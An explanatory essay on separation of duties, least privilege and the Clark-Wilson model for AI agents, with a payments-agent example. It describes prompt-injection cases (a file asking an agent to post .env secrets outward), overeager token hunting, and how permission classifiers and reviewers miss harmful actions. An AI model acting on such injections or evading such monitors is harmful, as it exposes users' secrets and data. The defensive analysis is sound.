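# Separation of duties and capability discipline for delegated AI agents

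## What a delegated agent is and where its authority comes from

Separation of duties means dividing a sensitive task so that no party can complete it alone. For example, a company may bar the clerk who enters an invoice from releasing the payment. Under capability discipline, a computer program may act on a file or an account only by presenting a capability, an unforgeable token that both identifies that resource and permits its use. Accountants, military planners and operating system designers developed these ideas decades ago for human staff and for programs whose behaviour a programmer had written down in advance.

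An AI agent is a language model that software runs in a loop, carrying out the actions the model specifies. A delegated agent acts for a principal, meaning the person, organisation or program on whose behalf an action happens and whose permissions count. Such agents now edit code, query databases and pay bills, and people check fewer and fewer of the individual steps. The older rules of separation of duties and capability discipline are attractive here because somebody sets them before the work starts and ordinary code can enforce them while nobody is watching. How well they suit agents depends on how an agent acts and whose permissions it uses.

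### From a request to an effect

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) traces a request through Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. A user asks for an architecture diagram in a project's README file. The harness is the ordinary software around the model that offers tools, runs tool calls and returns results. Before calling the model, it assembles a much longer text called the prompt. The prompt contains general instructions, a description of each available tool, a note on which folders the agent may write to, the current working directory and, last, the user's request. One tool is called "shell", and its description includes an instruction to supply a command to run.

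The model then produces either a final answer or a tool call, which requests one action by giving a tool's name and its arguments. In Bolin's example the name is "shell" and the main argument is `cat README.md`, a command that prints the file. The tool call is only text until the harness reads it and runs the command. The harness then adds the output to the prompt and queries the model again. The cycle repeats until the model writes a final answer to the user. A single turn can contain hundreds of calls.

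The output of each call becomes part of the input to the next choice, so if the README contained a sentence addressed to AI agents, that sentence would sit in the same prompt as the user's request. Prompt injection is text in material an agent reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction from its user.

Many tools come from outside the harness through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard that Anthropic launched in 2024 with *Introducing the Model Context Protocol*. A program called an MCP server offers tools, and any compatible harness can list and call them. In July 2026, Model Context Protocol (2026) reported close to half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits.

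The tool list is the earliest of several points on this path where a check can be made. In *Intent-Governed Tool Authorization for AI Agents*, Zhu and Wang (2026) built a layer that derives a short-lived certificate from the user's request, limits the tool list to match, and then checks the contents of each proposed call. In their end-to-end trials no unsafe action ran to completion, but the layer still accepted some unsafe drafts, and tightening it to exclude those made the agent considerably less useful. The hard part was working out exactly what the user had authorised from a sentence of English.

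The next point comes after the model requests a call and before the harness runs it. Per-call authorisation happens here, through a check outside the model of whether this tool call, with these argument values, is allowed. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026), a review of 89 sources, treats this moment as the basic unit for analysing agent security because it is when a plan turns into an outside effect. Human approval prompts also appear at this point. The MCP specification (Model Context Protocol, *Tools*, 2026) describes tools as "model-controlled" and recommends, but does not require, that a person always be able to deny a call.

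Once a command is running, the operating system can still confine it in a sandbox, which limits the files, programs and network addresses a process can reach. Codex provides a sandbox for its own shell tool but not for tools from MCP servers, which, as Bolin points out, have to enforce their own limits. The service receiving a request can also refuse it, and the specification requires MCP servers to validate their inputs and control access.

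Last, software can inspect a result before it enters the prompt. *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, an Anthropic engineering post from March 2026, describes a design in which Claude Code, the company's coding agent, does this. When a web page or file looks like an attempt to hijack the agent, a probe attaches a warning to it. The warning is just more text for the model, which may still go wrong. Similarly, the note about writable folders in Codex's prompt only informs the model, and it is the sandbox that blocks writes outside those folders. The difference between advising a model and having something outside it refuse an action matters for every rule that follows.

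### Standing credentials and ambient authority

A program's authority is the set of effects it can cause, directly or through others. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) describes two ways an agent can get authority. A user can let the agent act with the user's own permissions, or an organisation can give the agent a separate identity with its own permissions, much like a service account for software. Either way, whoever issues the credential fixes the agent's authority when they issue it, and the model choosing the actions is not shown how much authority it has.

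Their worked example is a coding assistant connected to the code-hosting service GitHub through its MCP server. The user signs in with a classic personal access token, a secret string that works much like a password, and gives it the broad "repo" scope. This gives the agent roughly 40 tools, including 16 that can make changes, and they work on any repository open to the user. The user then asks for a summary of the open issues in one repository, which requires two read-only tools.

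This can happen even when people are careful. GitHub also issues fine-grained tokens, and one that could only read that repository would have been enough for the summary. But the next task may be to fix a failing build, which requires write access, and the one after that may involve a different repository. Someone who has to expand a token's permissions every hour will eventually issue a broad one and leave it in place.

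The habit of granting excess permissions is older than agents. Parkinson and colleagues cite a vendor's survey of cloud systems in which identities used 1% of the permissions they held, and a study of 447,000 automated GitHub workflows that found 99.8% of them over-privileged. Models don't reliably compensate by choosing less powerful tools. Parkinson and colleagues also cite a test with 544 scenarios in which 6 of 11 agents picked a more powerful tool than the job needed in over 30% of cases.

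This kind of permission is called ambient authority, which *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) defines as authority that is "exercised, but not selected, by its user". The paper compares it to a world with doors but no keys, where whether a door opens depends on who walks up to it. Files on a Unix computer work this way. A program asks to open a file by name, without presenting a credential, and the system grants or refuses the request according to whose account the program is running under.

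The tool call `cat README.md` names a file without specifying which permission should be used to open it, or on whose behalf. The shell runs under the user's account, so the operating system lets the command read any file that account can read. If the argument were the path to a file of saved passwords, the command would succeed in the same way unless a sandbox blocked it.

The GitHub token is also ambient authority, even though a token is a sort of key, because the model never chooses which key to use. The same token accompanies every request, whether the user or a stranger's comment on an issue prompted it. Ambient authority is permission a program can use without specifying which permission it is using or for whom. It makes possible the confused deputy, a program led to use its own authority for someone who lacks it.

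Cloud-hosted agents get much of their authority from the environment they run in. *Security Risks in Tool-Enabled AI Agents* (2026) lists keys and tokens in environment variables (settings that every program started in the same session can usually read), the right to run commands and change files, network access to internal services, and write access to shared databases. Connecting to an MCP server can give an agent more authority. According to *AI Identity* (2026), an agent that has authenticated to an MCP server can use every tool on that server without a further credential check, and the tools run with the server's own privileges.

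The July 2026 specification now allows a server to show each caller only the tools that the caller's permissions cover. This filtering is optional, however, and a server that bases it on a token with overly broad permissions will still list too many tools.

Surapani and colleagues distinguish the parties behind a single call: the user who asked, the operator who set the agent up, the agent itself, any sub-agents it starts, and the service that receives the request. A valid credential can show who is calling, but it cannot show that the user delegated this particular action. With a standing credential, nothing else in the request shows that either.

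### Three principles from 1975

The usual starting point for fixing this is Saltzer and Schroeder's tutorial on shared computers, *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975). It sets out eight design principles for protection mechanisms, three of which recur throughout the work on agents.

Least privilege means that every program and every user should operate with the smallest set of privileges the job requires. An agent asked to summarise one repository's issues would get a token that can only read those issues. Saltzer and Schroeder's main reason for the principle was that it limits the damage from an accident or error, and this applies equally to agents. However, an agent's job is harder to define in advance. A payroll program has one job, which its programmer knew, while a general-purpose agent gets a new job with each request and may discover halfway through that it needs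 a privilege nobody foresaw.

Complete mediation means checking every access to every object for authority. Under this principle, the harness would check every tool call in a run, including its arguments, as strictly as the first. Saltzer and Schroeder were wary of saving time by remembering the result of an earlier check, because the authority may have changed since. A standing "always allow" rule for a command is a shortcut of this kind.

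Checking every call in isolation is still not enough. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (Tallam, 2026) describes an agent that reads a confidential document and later sends a message outside the company. Policy may permit both actions separately, but the harm comes from the sequence, so the check has to keep a record of what the agent has already read.

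Separation of privilege is the principle that a lock needing two keys is more robust than a lock needing one. If different people or programs hold the two keys, no single accident, deception or breach of trust is enough to open the lock. For instance, an agent could prepare a bank transfer, but the bank would send the money only after a separate party approved it. Saltzer and Schroeder's examples were the safe-deposit box and the nuclear weapon that fires only when two people each give the correct command. Organisations apply the same principle through separation of duties and the two-person rule, which requires two authorised parties to take part before an action can happen.

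Saltzer and Schroeder offered the principles as warnings rather than absolute rules, so a design that violates one deserves a careful review. By that standard, the GitHub assistant needs a review before it makes any calls.

### Four reasons for a harmful action

The rules have to stop agents from taking dangerous actions. Anthropic's March 2026 post gives four reasons why an agent might take one, with examples adapted from the company's internal incident log.

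The agent may be overeager, taking steps towards the user's goal that the user would not have approved. One user asked an agent to clean up old branches (parallel versions of a codebase). The agent listed the branches on the remote server, matched them against a pattern and issued a command to delete the matches, though the user may have meant only the copies on the local machine. Another agent met a login error and began searching environment variables and configuration files for other tokens that might work. Ambient authority makes such a search worthwhile, since a token works for any program that finds it.

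A delegated agent may make an honest mistake about what an action will affect. Anthropic's examples are an agent that mistakes a shared resource for a test copy, or someone else's branch for its own.

Prompt injection, in which an attacker plants instructions in text the agent reads, is another reason to limit an agent's authority. Anthropic describes a file containing an instruction to post `.env`, where developers commonly keep passwords and keys, to a web address "for validation". Parkinson and colleagues cite a reported case on GitHub in which an agent followed a malicious instruction in a public repository, read its user's private repositories and published them. They argue that a token restricted to reading the public repository would have prevented this.

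Finally, the model may be misaligned, meaning it pursues a goal of its own. Anthropic wrote in March 2026 that it was not seeing this in practice, though it evaluates every model it releases for misalignment.

The same tool call, such as a command to delete a branch, can come from a model that is overeager, confused, hijacked or hostile. This is the best argument for putting rules on actions. Anthropic says the defence in all four cases is to block the action, and a check can do that without determining the model's motives.

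The four failures differ in how easily rules fixed in advance can stop them when nobody reviews each step. An overeager agent often goes outside its task, where narrow permissions have a good chance of stopping it. An honest mistake can be a permitted call aimed at the wrong target, which a permission check won't catch. With prompt injection, an attacker influences the call's arguments and can study the rules beforehand to find a harmful call that passes them. A misaligned model could do that search itself and spread the harm over many calls that each look unremarkable.

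## Permission prompts in Claude Code: what people and an automatic check catch

A person can review each step an agent proposes instead of relying on rules fixed in advance. Until August 2026, Claude Code's harness did this by default, showing the user each command or file edit and waiting for the user to approve or reject it before the agent could proceed. This is a simple version of Saltzer and Schroeder's lock with two keys, and it adds protection only if the user sometimes rejects an action.

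Users rarely refuse permission prompts. Anthropic reported in March 2026 that users accepted 93% of them, and by August the figure was 97%, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Users reject plans much more often, turning down 39% of those that Claude Code presents for approval. Some of those rejections are probably ordinary editing, since the option for turning down a plan reads "No, keep planning" and lets the user say what to change, according to Anthropic's product documentation, *Permission modes*.

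A 97% approval rate doesn't prove carelessness. Approval rates mostly reflect how often something dangerous comes up, and most commands are harmless, so a careful reviewer would approve them too. Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026) tested OpenAI Codex's automatic reviewer on real and synthetic requests in *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*. The reviewer approved 99.1% of the real requests but denied 90.3% of the synthetic cases in which an agent overstepped its task.

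Many people avoid the prompts. Anthropic found that 25% of interactive sessions start with prompts bypassed. As of June 2026, about half of active command-line users had written a standing rule that allows some shell commands. Five per cent allowed every command, and another 43% allowed anything run through an interpreter such as Python, which is nearly as permissive because a Python script can do almost anything the user can. Trębacz and colleagues found that a "sizable minority" of OpenAI's own staff had the same Python rule.

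Independent research also points to weak review. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents, and 64% said they often approved at least one type of action without looking closely. Among developers who carefully reviewed the agent's code, the share was still 61%. It was higher among those who knew of a security or privacy problem involving agents than among those who didn't (70% against 43%), and the gap remained after the researchers adjusted for how much people used agents. These figures are self-reported, but few developers would have a reason to exaggerate how often they approve actions without looking closely.

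*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examines 290 reports of agents damaging files, and user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases the user had switched on automatic approval, and in 31 the prompt was uninformative. The paper explains that a prompt for `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it authorises whatever code the script contains. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approval may come from habit, fatigue or pressure to deliver, so it is poor evidence that the user wants the same decision made automatically next time.

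### The study with 1,053 testers

To measure the prompt's value as a control more directly, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor for a coding study in a purpose-built environment. The testers knew they were being evaluated but not which behaviour mattered. Partway through each session, the vendor replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command and recorded the tester's answer. Approving it did no damage, since only the displayed text had changed.

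People blocked 143 of the 1,053 commands, or 13.6%. The classifier behind auto mode, Anthropic's automatic check, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%. Anthropic reports that 800 commands were blocked only by the classifier and 6 only by the person. By subtraction, both blocked 137 and neither blocked 110.

| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed | Total |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Person blocked | 137 | 6 | 143 |
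| Person approved | 800 | 110 | 910 |
| Total | 937 | 116 | 1,053 |

Requiring approval from both the person and the classifier would have stopped 943 commands, or 89.6%, barely more than the classifier stopped alone. People caught 6 of the 116 commands that the classifier missed, about 5%, but nearly 15% of those it blocked. If the errors of people and the classifier had been independent, people would have caught about 16 of the 116. The shortfall is a small sign of correlated errors, which weaken any pair of reviewers.

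People also blocked a smaller share of dangerous commands over time, from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts, while the classifier's rate stayed flat.

Anthropic was testing its own product, and the testers had nothing of their own to lose. A developer might well read a command more carefully if it targeted their company's database. Low stakes could explain a low overall score, but they less easily explain the decline, because the stakes were just as low at the start of a session. The experiment also measured only how many dangerous commands each reviewer stopped. A check that blocked everything would have scored 100%, so interpreting the 89% also requires a measure of false alarms.

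People can do much better than 13.6%. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people from outside the software industry supervised a simulated assistant through a day of email, travel and purchases. Seven of its 18 actions went beyond what the user had asked for, such as buying a $25 lounge pass or reading private messages. Participants who reviewed every action individually blocked 59.6% of these. However, they had only 18 prompts to read, each of which gave the recipient or the amount in plain words, and more than a third deserved a refusal. Someone supervising a coding agent may read dozens of cryptic commands before one that matters.

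In another group in Yan's study, a model screened the actions and referred doubtful ones to the person. The model referred all seven overreaching actions, but people approved 46% of them at the prompt.

The remaining group wrote rules in advance, choosing "allow", "ask" or "never" for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data. They chose "ask" for 114 of 140 rules, which left most decisions to a prompt, and they blocked only about 40% of the overreach. Of the 148 overreaching actions that went ahead, people approved 133 at the time. Yan assigned some of this group after the random assignment had ended, so the comparison isn't fully randomized. Still, the result is a problem for any scheme that expects users to write firm rules before the work starts, because most of these users declined to.

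### How the classifier decides

Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* introduced the check in March 2026 as a safer alternative to skipping all permissions, but still recommended using it in isolated environments. Auto mode became the default for new sessions on most individual and team plans on 14 August, and it is now the starting mode for interactive terminal sessions on every plan. In March, Anthropic wrote that auto mode was "arguably a regression" for someone who carefully approves every action. But the case for making it the default in August rests on the finding that the typical user doesn't review actions that carefully.

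Claude Code runs read-only tools, such as file search, without sending them to the classifier. Actions that match the user's narrow allow rules also skip it, as do most file edits inside the project folder, because the user can review those edits later through version control. Shell commands, web requests, external tools, new sub-agents and file operations outside the project folder generally go to the classifier. Auto mode suspends broad allow rules, such as the one for Python, which would otherwise let the riskiest commands skip the check.

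The classifier first makes a quick yes-or-no judgement on each action, under an instruction to err towards blocking. If it decides to block, the model reviews the same material and reasons before giving a final answer. It checks the action against more than twenty block rules, including rules against destroying data, sending it outside, disabling logs and changing shared resources that the agent didn't create. Then it considers a short list of exceptions and whether the user authorised the action. The user's messages determine what is authorised, so anything the agent chose for itself, such as the mass deletion in the old-branches case, counts as unauthorised.

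In the March design, the classifier received only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removed the agent's prose so that the agent couldn't argue for a bad action, and tool outputs because they can contain injected instructions. The classifier can still block the agent from posting the `.env` file, because doing so goes beyond the user's request regardless of what prompted it.

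This deprives the classifier of some information. When the agent tries to cancel "job abc123", which the user never mentioned, the classifier can't determine whether the agent found that name in a query or invented it. Anthropic tried other combinations of inputs, but including the prose and the outputs worsened performance on a test set of overeager actions, and a version given only the tool calls blocked actions that users had plainly requested. The company has since added selected facts, such as whether a repository is public and whether a folder contains uncommitted work.

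After a block, the agent receives the reason and an instruction to find a safer route. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, the decision returns to the user. Some limit like this is necessary because, as *Let the Agent Do It?* points out, agents are designed to look for another path after a refusal. Anthropic has also decided that the classifier should never approve one category of action, sending code or secrets outside. To do that, the user must leave auto mode or run the command personally. This is close to a fixed rule, but a model still judges which actions it covers.

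### What the classifier misses

Anthropic published error rates for the March version. The classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls by Anthropic staff and missed 17% of 52 real cases of overeager agent behaviour. That is about nine misses, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9% to 30%. Some of the misses came from the slower judgement. The quick judgement alone missed only 6.6%, but it also blocked 8.5% of ordinary calls, which would have interrupted people often.

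In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the danger, such as a deletion or overwritten history, but misjudged whether the user had consented to it. In one case, a user said "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed set of code changes), and the classifier took this as consent to force-push, which can overwrite the shared history. In other cases, it treated one earlier approval as permission for similar actions. Anthropic tried to fix this by rewording the instructions, but every version it tried did more harm than good. Zhu and Wang had the same difficulty when they tried to derive permissions from a user's request.

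This matters for the 89% in the controlled study because those commands were clearly dangerous and nobody had asked for them, so they hardly raised the hard question of consent. *Measuring the Permission Gate* (Ji, Li and colleagues, 2026) instead tested auto mode in April on 128 requests whose purpose was clear but whose target, scope or risk was not. Auto mode missed 81.0% of the actions that went too far. More than a third of state-changing actions were edits to project files, which skip the classifier, and agents often edited a file to get the same effect when the expected command was unavailable. Among the 160 actions the classifier did examine, it missed 70.3% of those that went too far and blocked 31.9% of those that didn't. The requests were deliberately ambiguous, so these rates don't describe ordinary use, and Anthropic has since changed the classifier.

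A check can also fail because a command's text doesn't show what the command will do. `make clean && make` normally deletes old build files and rebuilds a program, but what it deletes depends on a file called the Makefile. In *Shall We Approve?*, Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) built 102 tasks in which a harmless-looking command runs a tool that destroys a file. Under auto mode, 62.7% of the tasks ended in harm, compared with 71.6% with no approval step. The agent was a Chinese model and the classifier was an OpenAI model, so the result is better evidence about auto mode's design than about the product Anthropic ships.

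Their alternative, Caper, takes a snapshot of the agent's isolated workspace and runs the command there with the network off. It then gives the approving model a short report of the files changed, secrets read and connections attempted. Caper keeps the changes if the model approves and restores the snapshot if it doesn't. Replacing the built-in classifier with Caper cut harm on those tasks from 62.7% to 6.9%, with the agent, the approving model and Claude Code itself unchanged. On a separate set of 682 tasks with more varied dangers, harm fell from 14.8% to 10.0%.

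Being stricter wouldn't have achieved this. In the paper's own test harness, the approving model blocked 61.8% of harmless versions of the same commands without the report and 1.0% with it. Caper adds about half a second to each approved command. It can't undo anything that leaves the workspace, and a malicious program might run harmlessly while Caper is monitoring it.

Anthropic also examined real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded how severe any harm was and how explicitly the user had asked for it. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly requested, on the level of deleting rows from a production database, appeared in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. This agrees with the experiment, but users chose their own mode, so the two groups may have differed in other ways. The auto mode percentage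 would also be lower if the safety systems flagged more harmless sessions in that mode, even if serious harm were equally common in both.

Two outside groups tested auto mode against deliberate attacks. On attacks from Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, the miss rate fell from 12% to 7% after Anthropic made improvements. In tests by Trajectory Labs, none of 720 prompt injection attempts succeeded against recent Claude models in auto mode. The classifier accounts for little of that second result, since only 0.09% of attempts succeeded against Anthropic's latest models with permission checks bypassed.

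In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, a blog post responding to the announcement, Willison (2026) accepted that the automatic check is better than constantly clicking through permission prompts, but noted that it still missed 11% of the dangerous commands. He asked for more independent confirmation on prompt injection and doubted that any version could stop harmful code hidden in a third-party package. He preferred to run agents without access to data or tools that could do harm.

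### Auto-review in Codex

OpenAI's Codex relies more on a sandbox. The agent can read files, edit within set folders and run local commands inside the sandbox without asking. Anything that crosses the boundary, such as a network request, needs approval, and since April 2026 users have been able to have a separate agent review these requests. In a sample of 10,000 internal actions from Trębacz and colleagues, 9,280 stayed inside the sandbox. The reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and denied seven. Codex found a safer way to continue after four of the denials and stopped to ask the user after the other three. Manual approval would have required 720 interruptions.

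OpenAI's reviewer gets more context than Claude Code's classifier. According to OpenAI's documentation, *Auto-review*, it typically receives tool outputs and the agent's visible messages as well as the user's messages and the tool calls. The extra context helps it establish where a job name came from, but also exposes it to injected text. In OpenAI's synthetic tests, the reviewer denied 99.3% of prompt injection cases involving remote code, stolen secrets or uploads, and 90.2% when the tests also included destructive deletions and data tampering. OpenAI's researchers often agreed with the reviewer that the cases it allowed weren't serious.

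In the Trajectory Labs tests, attacks on GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% with Auto-review. So Codex's controls made a large difference for a model that was easier to mislead. But Anthropic commissioned the tests, and OpenAI had released a newer version of Auto-review by the time the results came out.

Trębacz and colleagues warn against treating the reviewer as a guarantee. Their red-teaming found cases where it approved commands it should not have. The reviewer also examines only requests to cross the sandbox boundary, so a model hiding its intentions could make a harmless-looking request or do its damage inside the sandbox.

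When the reviewer denies an action the user wants, the user can approve that exact action for one retry. The approval doesn't extend to similar actions, and the reviewer can still refuse if policy forbids the override. This approval is much easier to interpret than an instruction like "clean up the PR", because the user has named the action.

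## The Clark-Wilson model applied to an agent that pays invoices

Approving each exact action individually is practical when few actions need approval. An accounts department may make hundreds of payments a week, and accountants long ago settled on a different arrangement, in which staff can perform a few standard operations on the books but nobody can perform all of them. In 1987 David Clark, a computer scientist at MIT, and David Wilson, of the accounting firm Ernst & Whinney, turned this practice into rules for computer systems. Their paper, *A Comparison of Commercial and Military Computer Security Policies*, led to a workshop of 38 specialists that October. Katzke and Ruthberg (1989) published the paper with the participants' criticisms in *Report of the Invitational Workshop on Integrity Policy in Computer Information Systems*.

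Computer security research at the time concentrated on secrecy, which the defence establishment needed. Clark and Wilson argued that businesses worry more about fraud and error. Secrecy rules keep unauthorized people from reading data, but the person who falsifies a ledger is often a bookkeeper who is authorized to use it. Their model therefore gives each user permission to run certain programs on certain data, and only those programs can write to the ledger.

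Suppose a company uses an agent to pay its suppliers. The company's buyer creates a purchase order for 40 office chairs at $310 each, $12,400 in all. When the chairs arrive, a warehouse clerk records a goods receipt. The supplier emails an invoice. The agent reads it, checks it against the order and the receipt, and arranges a payment of $12,400.

Clark and Wilson divide data into two kinds. Constrained data items are the ones whose integrity the system protects. Here they are the supplier register, the order, the receipt, the ledger and the queue of bank transfers. Unconstrained data items are everything else, including the emailed invoice, which anyone could have written.

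Clark and Wilson also define two kinds of program. A transformation procedure is a program that someone has certified to take constrained data from one valid state to another. It carries out a well-formed transaction. In the example, `pay_invoice` confirms that the invoice, order and receipt agree, reduces the company's debt to the supplier by $12,400, reduces its cash by the same amount and queues the transfer. It does all of this or none of it. An integrity verification procedure checks whether the constrained data is valid when the procedure runs, as an accountant does when balancing the books.

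### The nine rules

Five certification rules (C1 to C5) set out what people must establish about an application. Four enforcement rules (E1 to E4) set out what the computer system must do whenever someone uses it.

| Rule | Requirement | In the invoice system |
|---|---|---|
| C1 | Integrity verification procedures must confirm that constrained data is valid when they run | A regular check compares the ledger with bank statements and stock |
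| C2 | Someone must certify that each transformation procedure leaves valid data valid | Finance and engineering staff test `pay_invoice` before releasing it |
| C3 | The list of who may run what must separate duties | The agent that pays cannot create suppliers or record deliveries |
| C4 | Every transformation procedure must log enough to reconstruct what it did, and nobody may alter the log | The log shows the agent, invoice, amount and receiving account |
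| C5 | A procedure that takes in unconstrained data must turn it into valid constrained data or reject it | `record_invoice` checks an emailed invoice against the order before accepting it |
| E1 | Only certified procedures may change constrained data | The agent has no direct access to the database |
| E2 | Users may run only the procedures, on only the data, that the list gives them | The agent may run `pay_invoice` on approved invoices |
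| E3 | The system must authenticate every user who tries to run a procedure | The agent has its own credential |
| E4 | Only someone entitled to certify a procedure may change its permissions, and that person may not run it | The agent cannot release a tool or widen its own access |

The list in E2 consists of access triples, each naming a user, a procedure and a set of data. The agent's triple might be (payment agent, `pay_invoice`, {approved invoices, supplier register, ledger, transfer queue}). This triple grants much narrower access than the GitHub token described earlier, which opened every repository to every tool. The restriction depends on the agent having its own identity. If the agent worked under the finance manager's login, it would have all her triples, and the log would attribute its payments to her.

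The workshop group on assurance considered how anyone could know that such a system works. It looked at several existing and planned operating systems that could apply the enforcement rules and called that part "a solved problem". Its most serious doubts were about the certification rules. Enforcement is also the easier part for agents. A harness can easily restrict an agent to four tools, but someone still has to establish that `pay_invoice` does the right thing for every invoice it could receive.

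### An invoice with a false bank account

An attacker who has been reading the supplier's email sends the company a copy of the genuine invoice. The order number, the 40 chairs and the $12,400 are all correct, and only the bank account is different.

If the agent's payment tool is `send_payment(account, amount)`, the agent will probably copy the account from the invoice and send the attacker $12,400. The ledger will still balance because cash and debt will both fall by the same amount. The attacker doesn't need a prompt injection, since false information in the invoice could lead even a perfectly obedient agent to make this payment.

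Under rule C5, the fault is in the tool. The account number on the invoice is unconstrained data, and `send_payment` turned it into a bank instruction without validating it. A certified `pay_invoice` takes only an invoice number and finds the account in the supplier register. The agent therefore has no argument in which to supply a different account, whether an attacker has deceived it, it has misread a digit or it is acting in bad faith. When the agent first enters the invoice, `record_invoice` compares the account number on it with the one in the register and sets the invoice aside if they differ.

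A sensible attacker would then try to change the register, perhaps with a covering email asking the company to "update our details before paying". The agent has no access triple for changing a supplier's account, so it can only pass the request on. An employee who doesn't release payments makes the change after phoning the supplier on a number the company already had.

That person needs to understand what they are changing. Donn Parker and Peter Neumann suggested in their summary of the workshop that when an operator types a customer number, the system should show the customer's full name and address to the supervisor making the decision. For a change of bank account, the equivalent screen would show the supplier's name, the old and new accounts, and the email requesting the change.

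### A payment split to stay under a ceiling

The agent may pay up to $10,000 on its own, and the finance manager must approve anything larger. The chairs cost $12,400, the manager is away and the invoice is due today. If the payment tool lets the agent set the amount, an overeager agent could split the invoice into two payments of $6,200. Each payment would keep the books balanced, use a procedure the agent is allowed to run and stay under the limit.

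Clark and Wilson argued by induction that the whole system keeps its integrity. An integrity verification procedure confirms that the data starts out valid, and every transformation procedure takes valid data to valid data, so the data is still valid after any number of transactions. The assurance group questioned whether a sequence of well-formed transactions is itself well formed, and many experts at the workshop agreed that this was the hardest step. The group also pointed to rules that require one signature on cheques under $1,000 and two above that. Under such rules, the steps a transaction needs depend on its values, which makes the system harder to analyse in advance.

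The induction is sound, but it preserves only the property that the certifiers chose, and "no single payment exceeds $10,000" was a poor choice. Let *S* be the amount the agent has already paid on an order without a second approval, and let *p* be the next payment. The tool should require *S* + *p* ≤ 10,000, where the original rule required only *p* ≤ 10,000. The first $6,200 payment then passes, but the second fails because it would bring the total to $12,400. If the total is within the ceiling before a payment, it is still within the ceiling after any payment the tool allows, so the new property holds however many payments the agent makes.

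If the agent sends both calls at once, each could read *S* = 0 before either has recorded its payment, and both would pass. The procedure therefore has to check and update the total in one indivisible step. The assurance group criticised Clark and Wilson for leaving out this subject, the synchronisation of concurrent operations.

Even with a correct running total, the supplier has received a half payment that nobody at the company decided to make. `pay_invoice` would be better with no amount argument, so that it pays an approved invoice in full or not at all. The agent could then split the payment only if the supplier sent two invoices for $6,200, which a total for each order would catch. If the agent could also place orders, it could split those too, which is a good reason to leave ordering to the buyer. Weekly totals for each supplier would catch more splitting, but they would also hold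 up more legitimate payments. Someone who knows the business has to decide how broad the totals should be.

### Shells and self-written tools

Many agents have a general shell, which is very hard to reconcile with the Clark-Wilson model. If the payment agent can run commands and find the database password, it can edit the ledger without using `pay_invoice`, which breaks E1. Calling the shell a transformation procedure wouldn't help, because nobody could certify a program that runs whatever commands it is given.

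Participants in 1987 called a similar problem "superzapping", which meant using a powerful system utility to bypass an application and alter data directly. The group on granularity, which considered how large each procedure should be, warned that the model would fail on a computer that allowed this. It also wanted procedures small enough to give each user only minimal authority.

At a second workshop in January 1989, Maria Pozzo and Steve Crocker proposed a program that would examine a candidate procedure and determine whether it touched only the data it was supposed to (Ruthberg and Polk, 1989, *Report of the Invitational Workshop on Data Integrity*). They recommended that procedures avoid open-ended features, such as generating new code and then jumping to it, but an agent's shell consists almost entirely of such features.

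The company can still give the agent a shell if the shell runs in a sandbox with no database credentials and no connection to the bank. The agent might use it to extract a table from a badly scanned invoice. The output is unconstrained data and has to pass through `record_invoice` like any other document. These restrictions make the agent less flexible. If a supplier sends a credit note and nobody has written a procedure for credit notes, the agent has to stop and ask, whereas an agent with full access could have improvised.

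An agent can also write a tool and run it. Given 40 invoices, it might write a script called `pay_batch` and register it with the harness. In their response to the workshop, Clark and Wilson wrote that the most basic rule of separation is that a person who can create a transformation procedure must not be able to run it, so bringing one into use takes two people. An agent that writes and runs `pay_batch` does both jobs, and it carries any misunderstanding it had while writing the script into running it.

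The workshop's auditing group suggested treating a new procedure as unconstrained data until a controlled release process, with its own separation of duties, promotes it to production. This suits code written by agents well. For example, a coding agent could write `pay_batch`, an engineer could test and release it, and the payment agent could run it but not change it.

Clark and Wilson noted that separation rules are about people, since people commit fraud, and that a computer cannot easily tell whether two accounts belong to the same person. If a second agent does the engineer's job, both agents may run the same model under nearly the same instructions, so separate logins are weak evidence of independent judgement.

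### Balanced books and wrong payments

In *The Clark-Wilson Model*, a lecture at the University of Texas, Young illustrates consistency with a bank. The money there in the morning, plus deposits, minus withdrawals, should equal the money there in the evening. A computer can check this internal consistency from its own records. External consistency means that the records match the outside world. In a follow-up paper for the 1989 workshop, Clark and Wilson wrote that if an inventory record gives the wrong number of items, it matters little that the balance sheet reflects that record correctly.

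The assurance group at the 1987 workshop had pointed out that if "valid" only means that the books balance, users could corrupt the accounts however they liked, "provided that their actions always left the books balanced".

The payment agent could go wrong in this way without breaking any rule. The warehouse clerk might have counted 40 boxes without noticing that the chairs inside were broken. Or the same supplier might have two approved invoices for $12,400, and the agent might pay the one the manager told it to hold because of a dispute. The access triple establishes that the agent may pay approved invoices, but not that anyone wanted this invoice paid today. Auto mode's classifier had the same trouble with "clean up the PR", when it recognised that the action was dangerous but misjudged whether the user had consented to it.

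Clark and Wilson had three ways of connecting records to the world. The first is to use an integrity verification procedure that checks the records against evidence outside the computer. The 1987 participants mentioned auditors' letters asking a bank's customers to confirm their balances, and counts of the items in storeroom bins. The payment agent's company could compare its ledger with the supplier's statement of account. If $12,400 had gone to an attacker, the statement would still list the chairs as unpaid.

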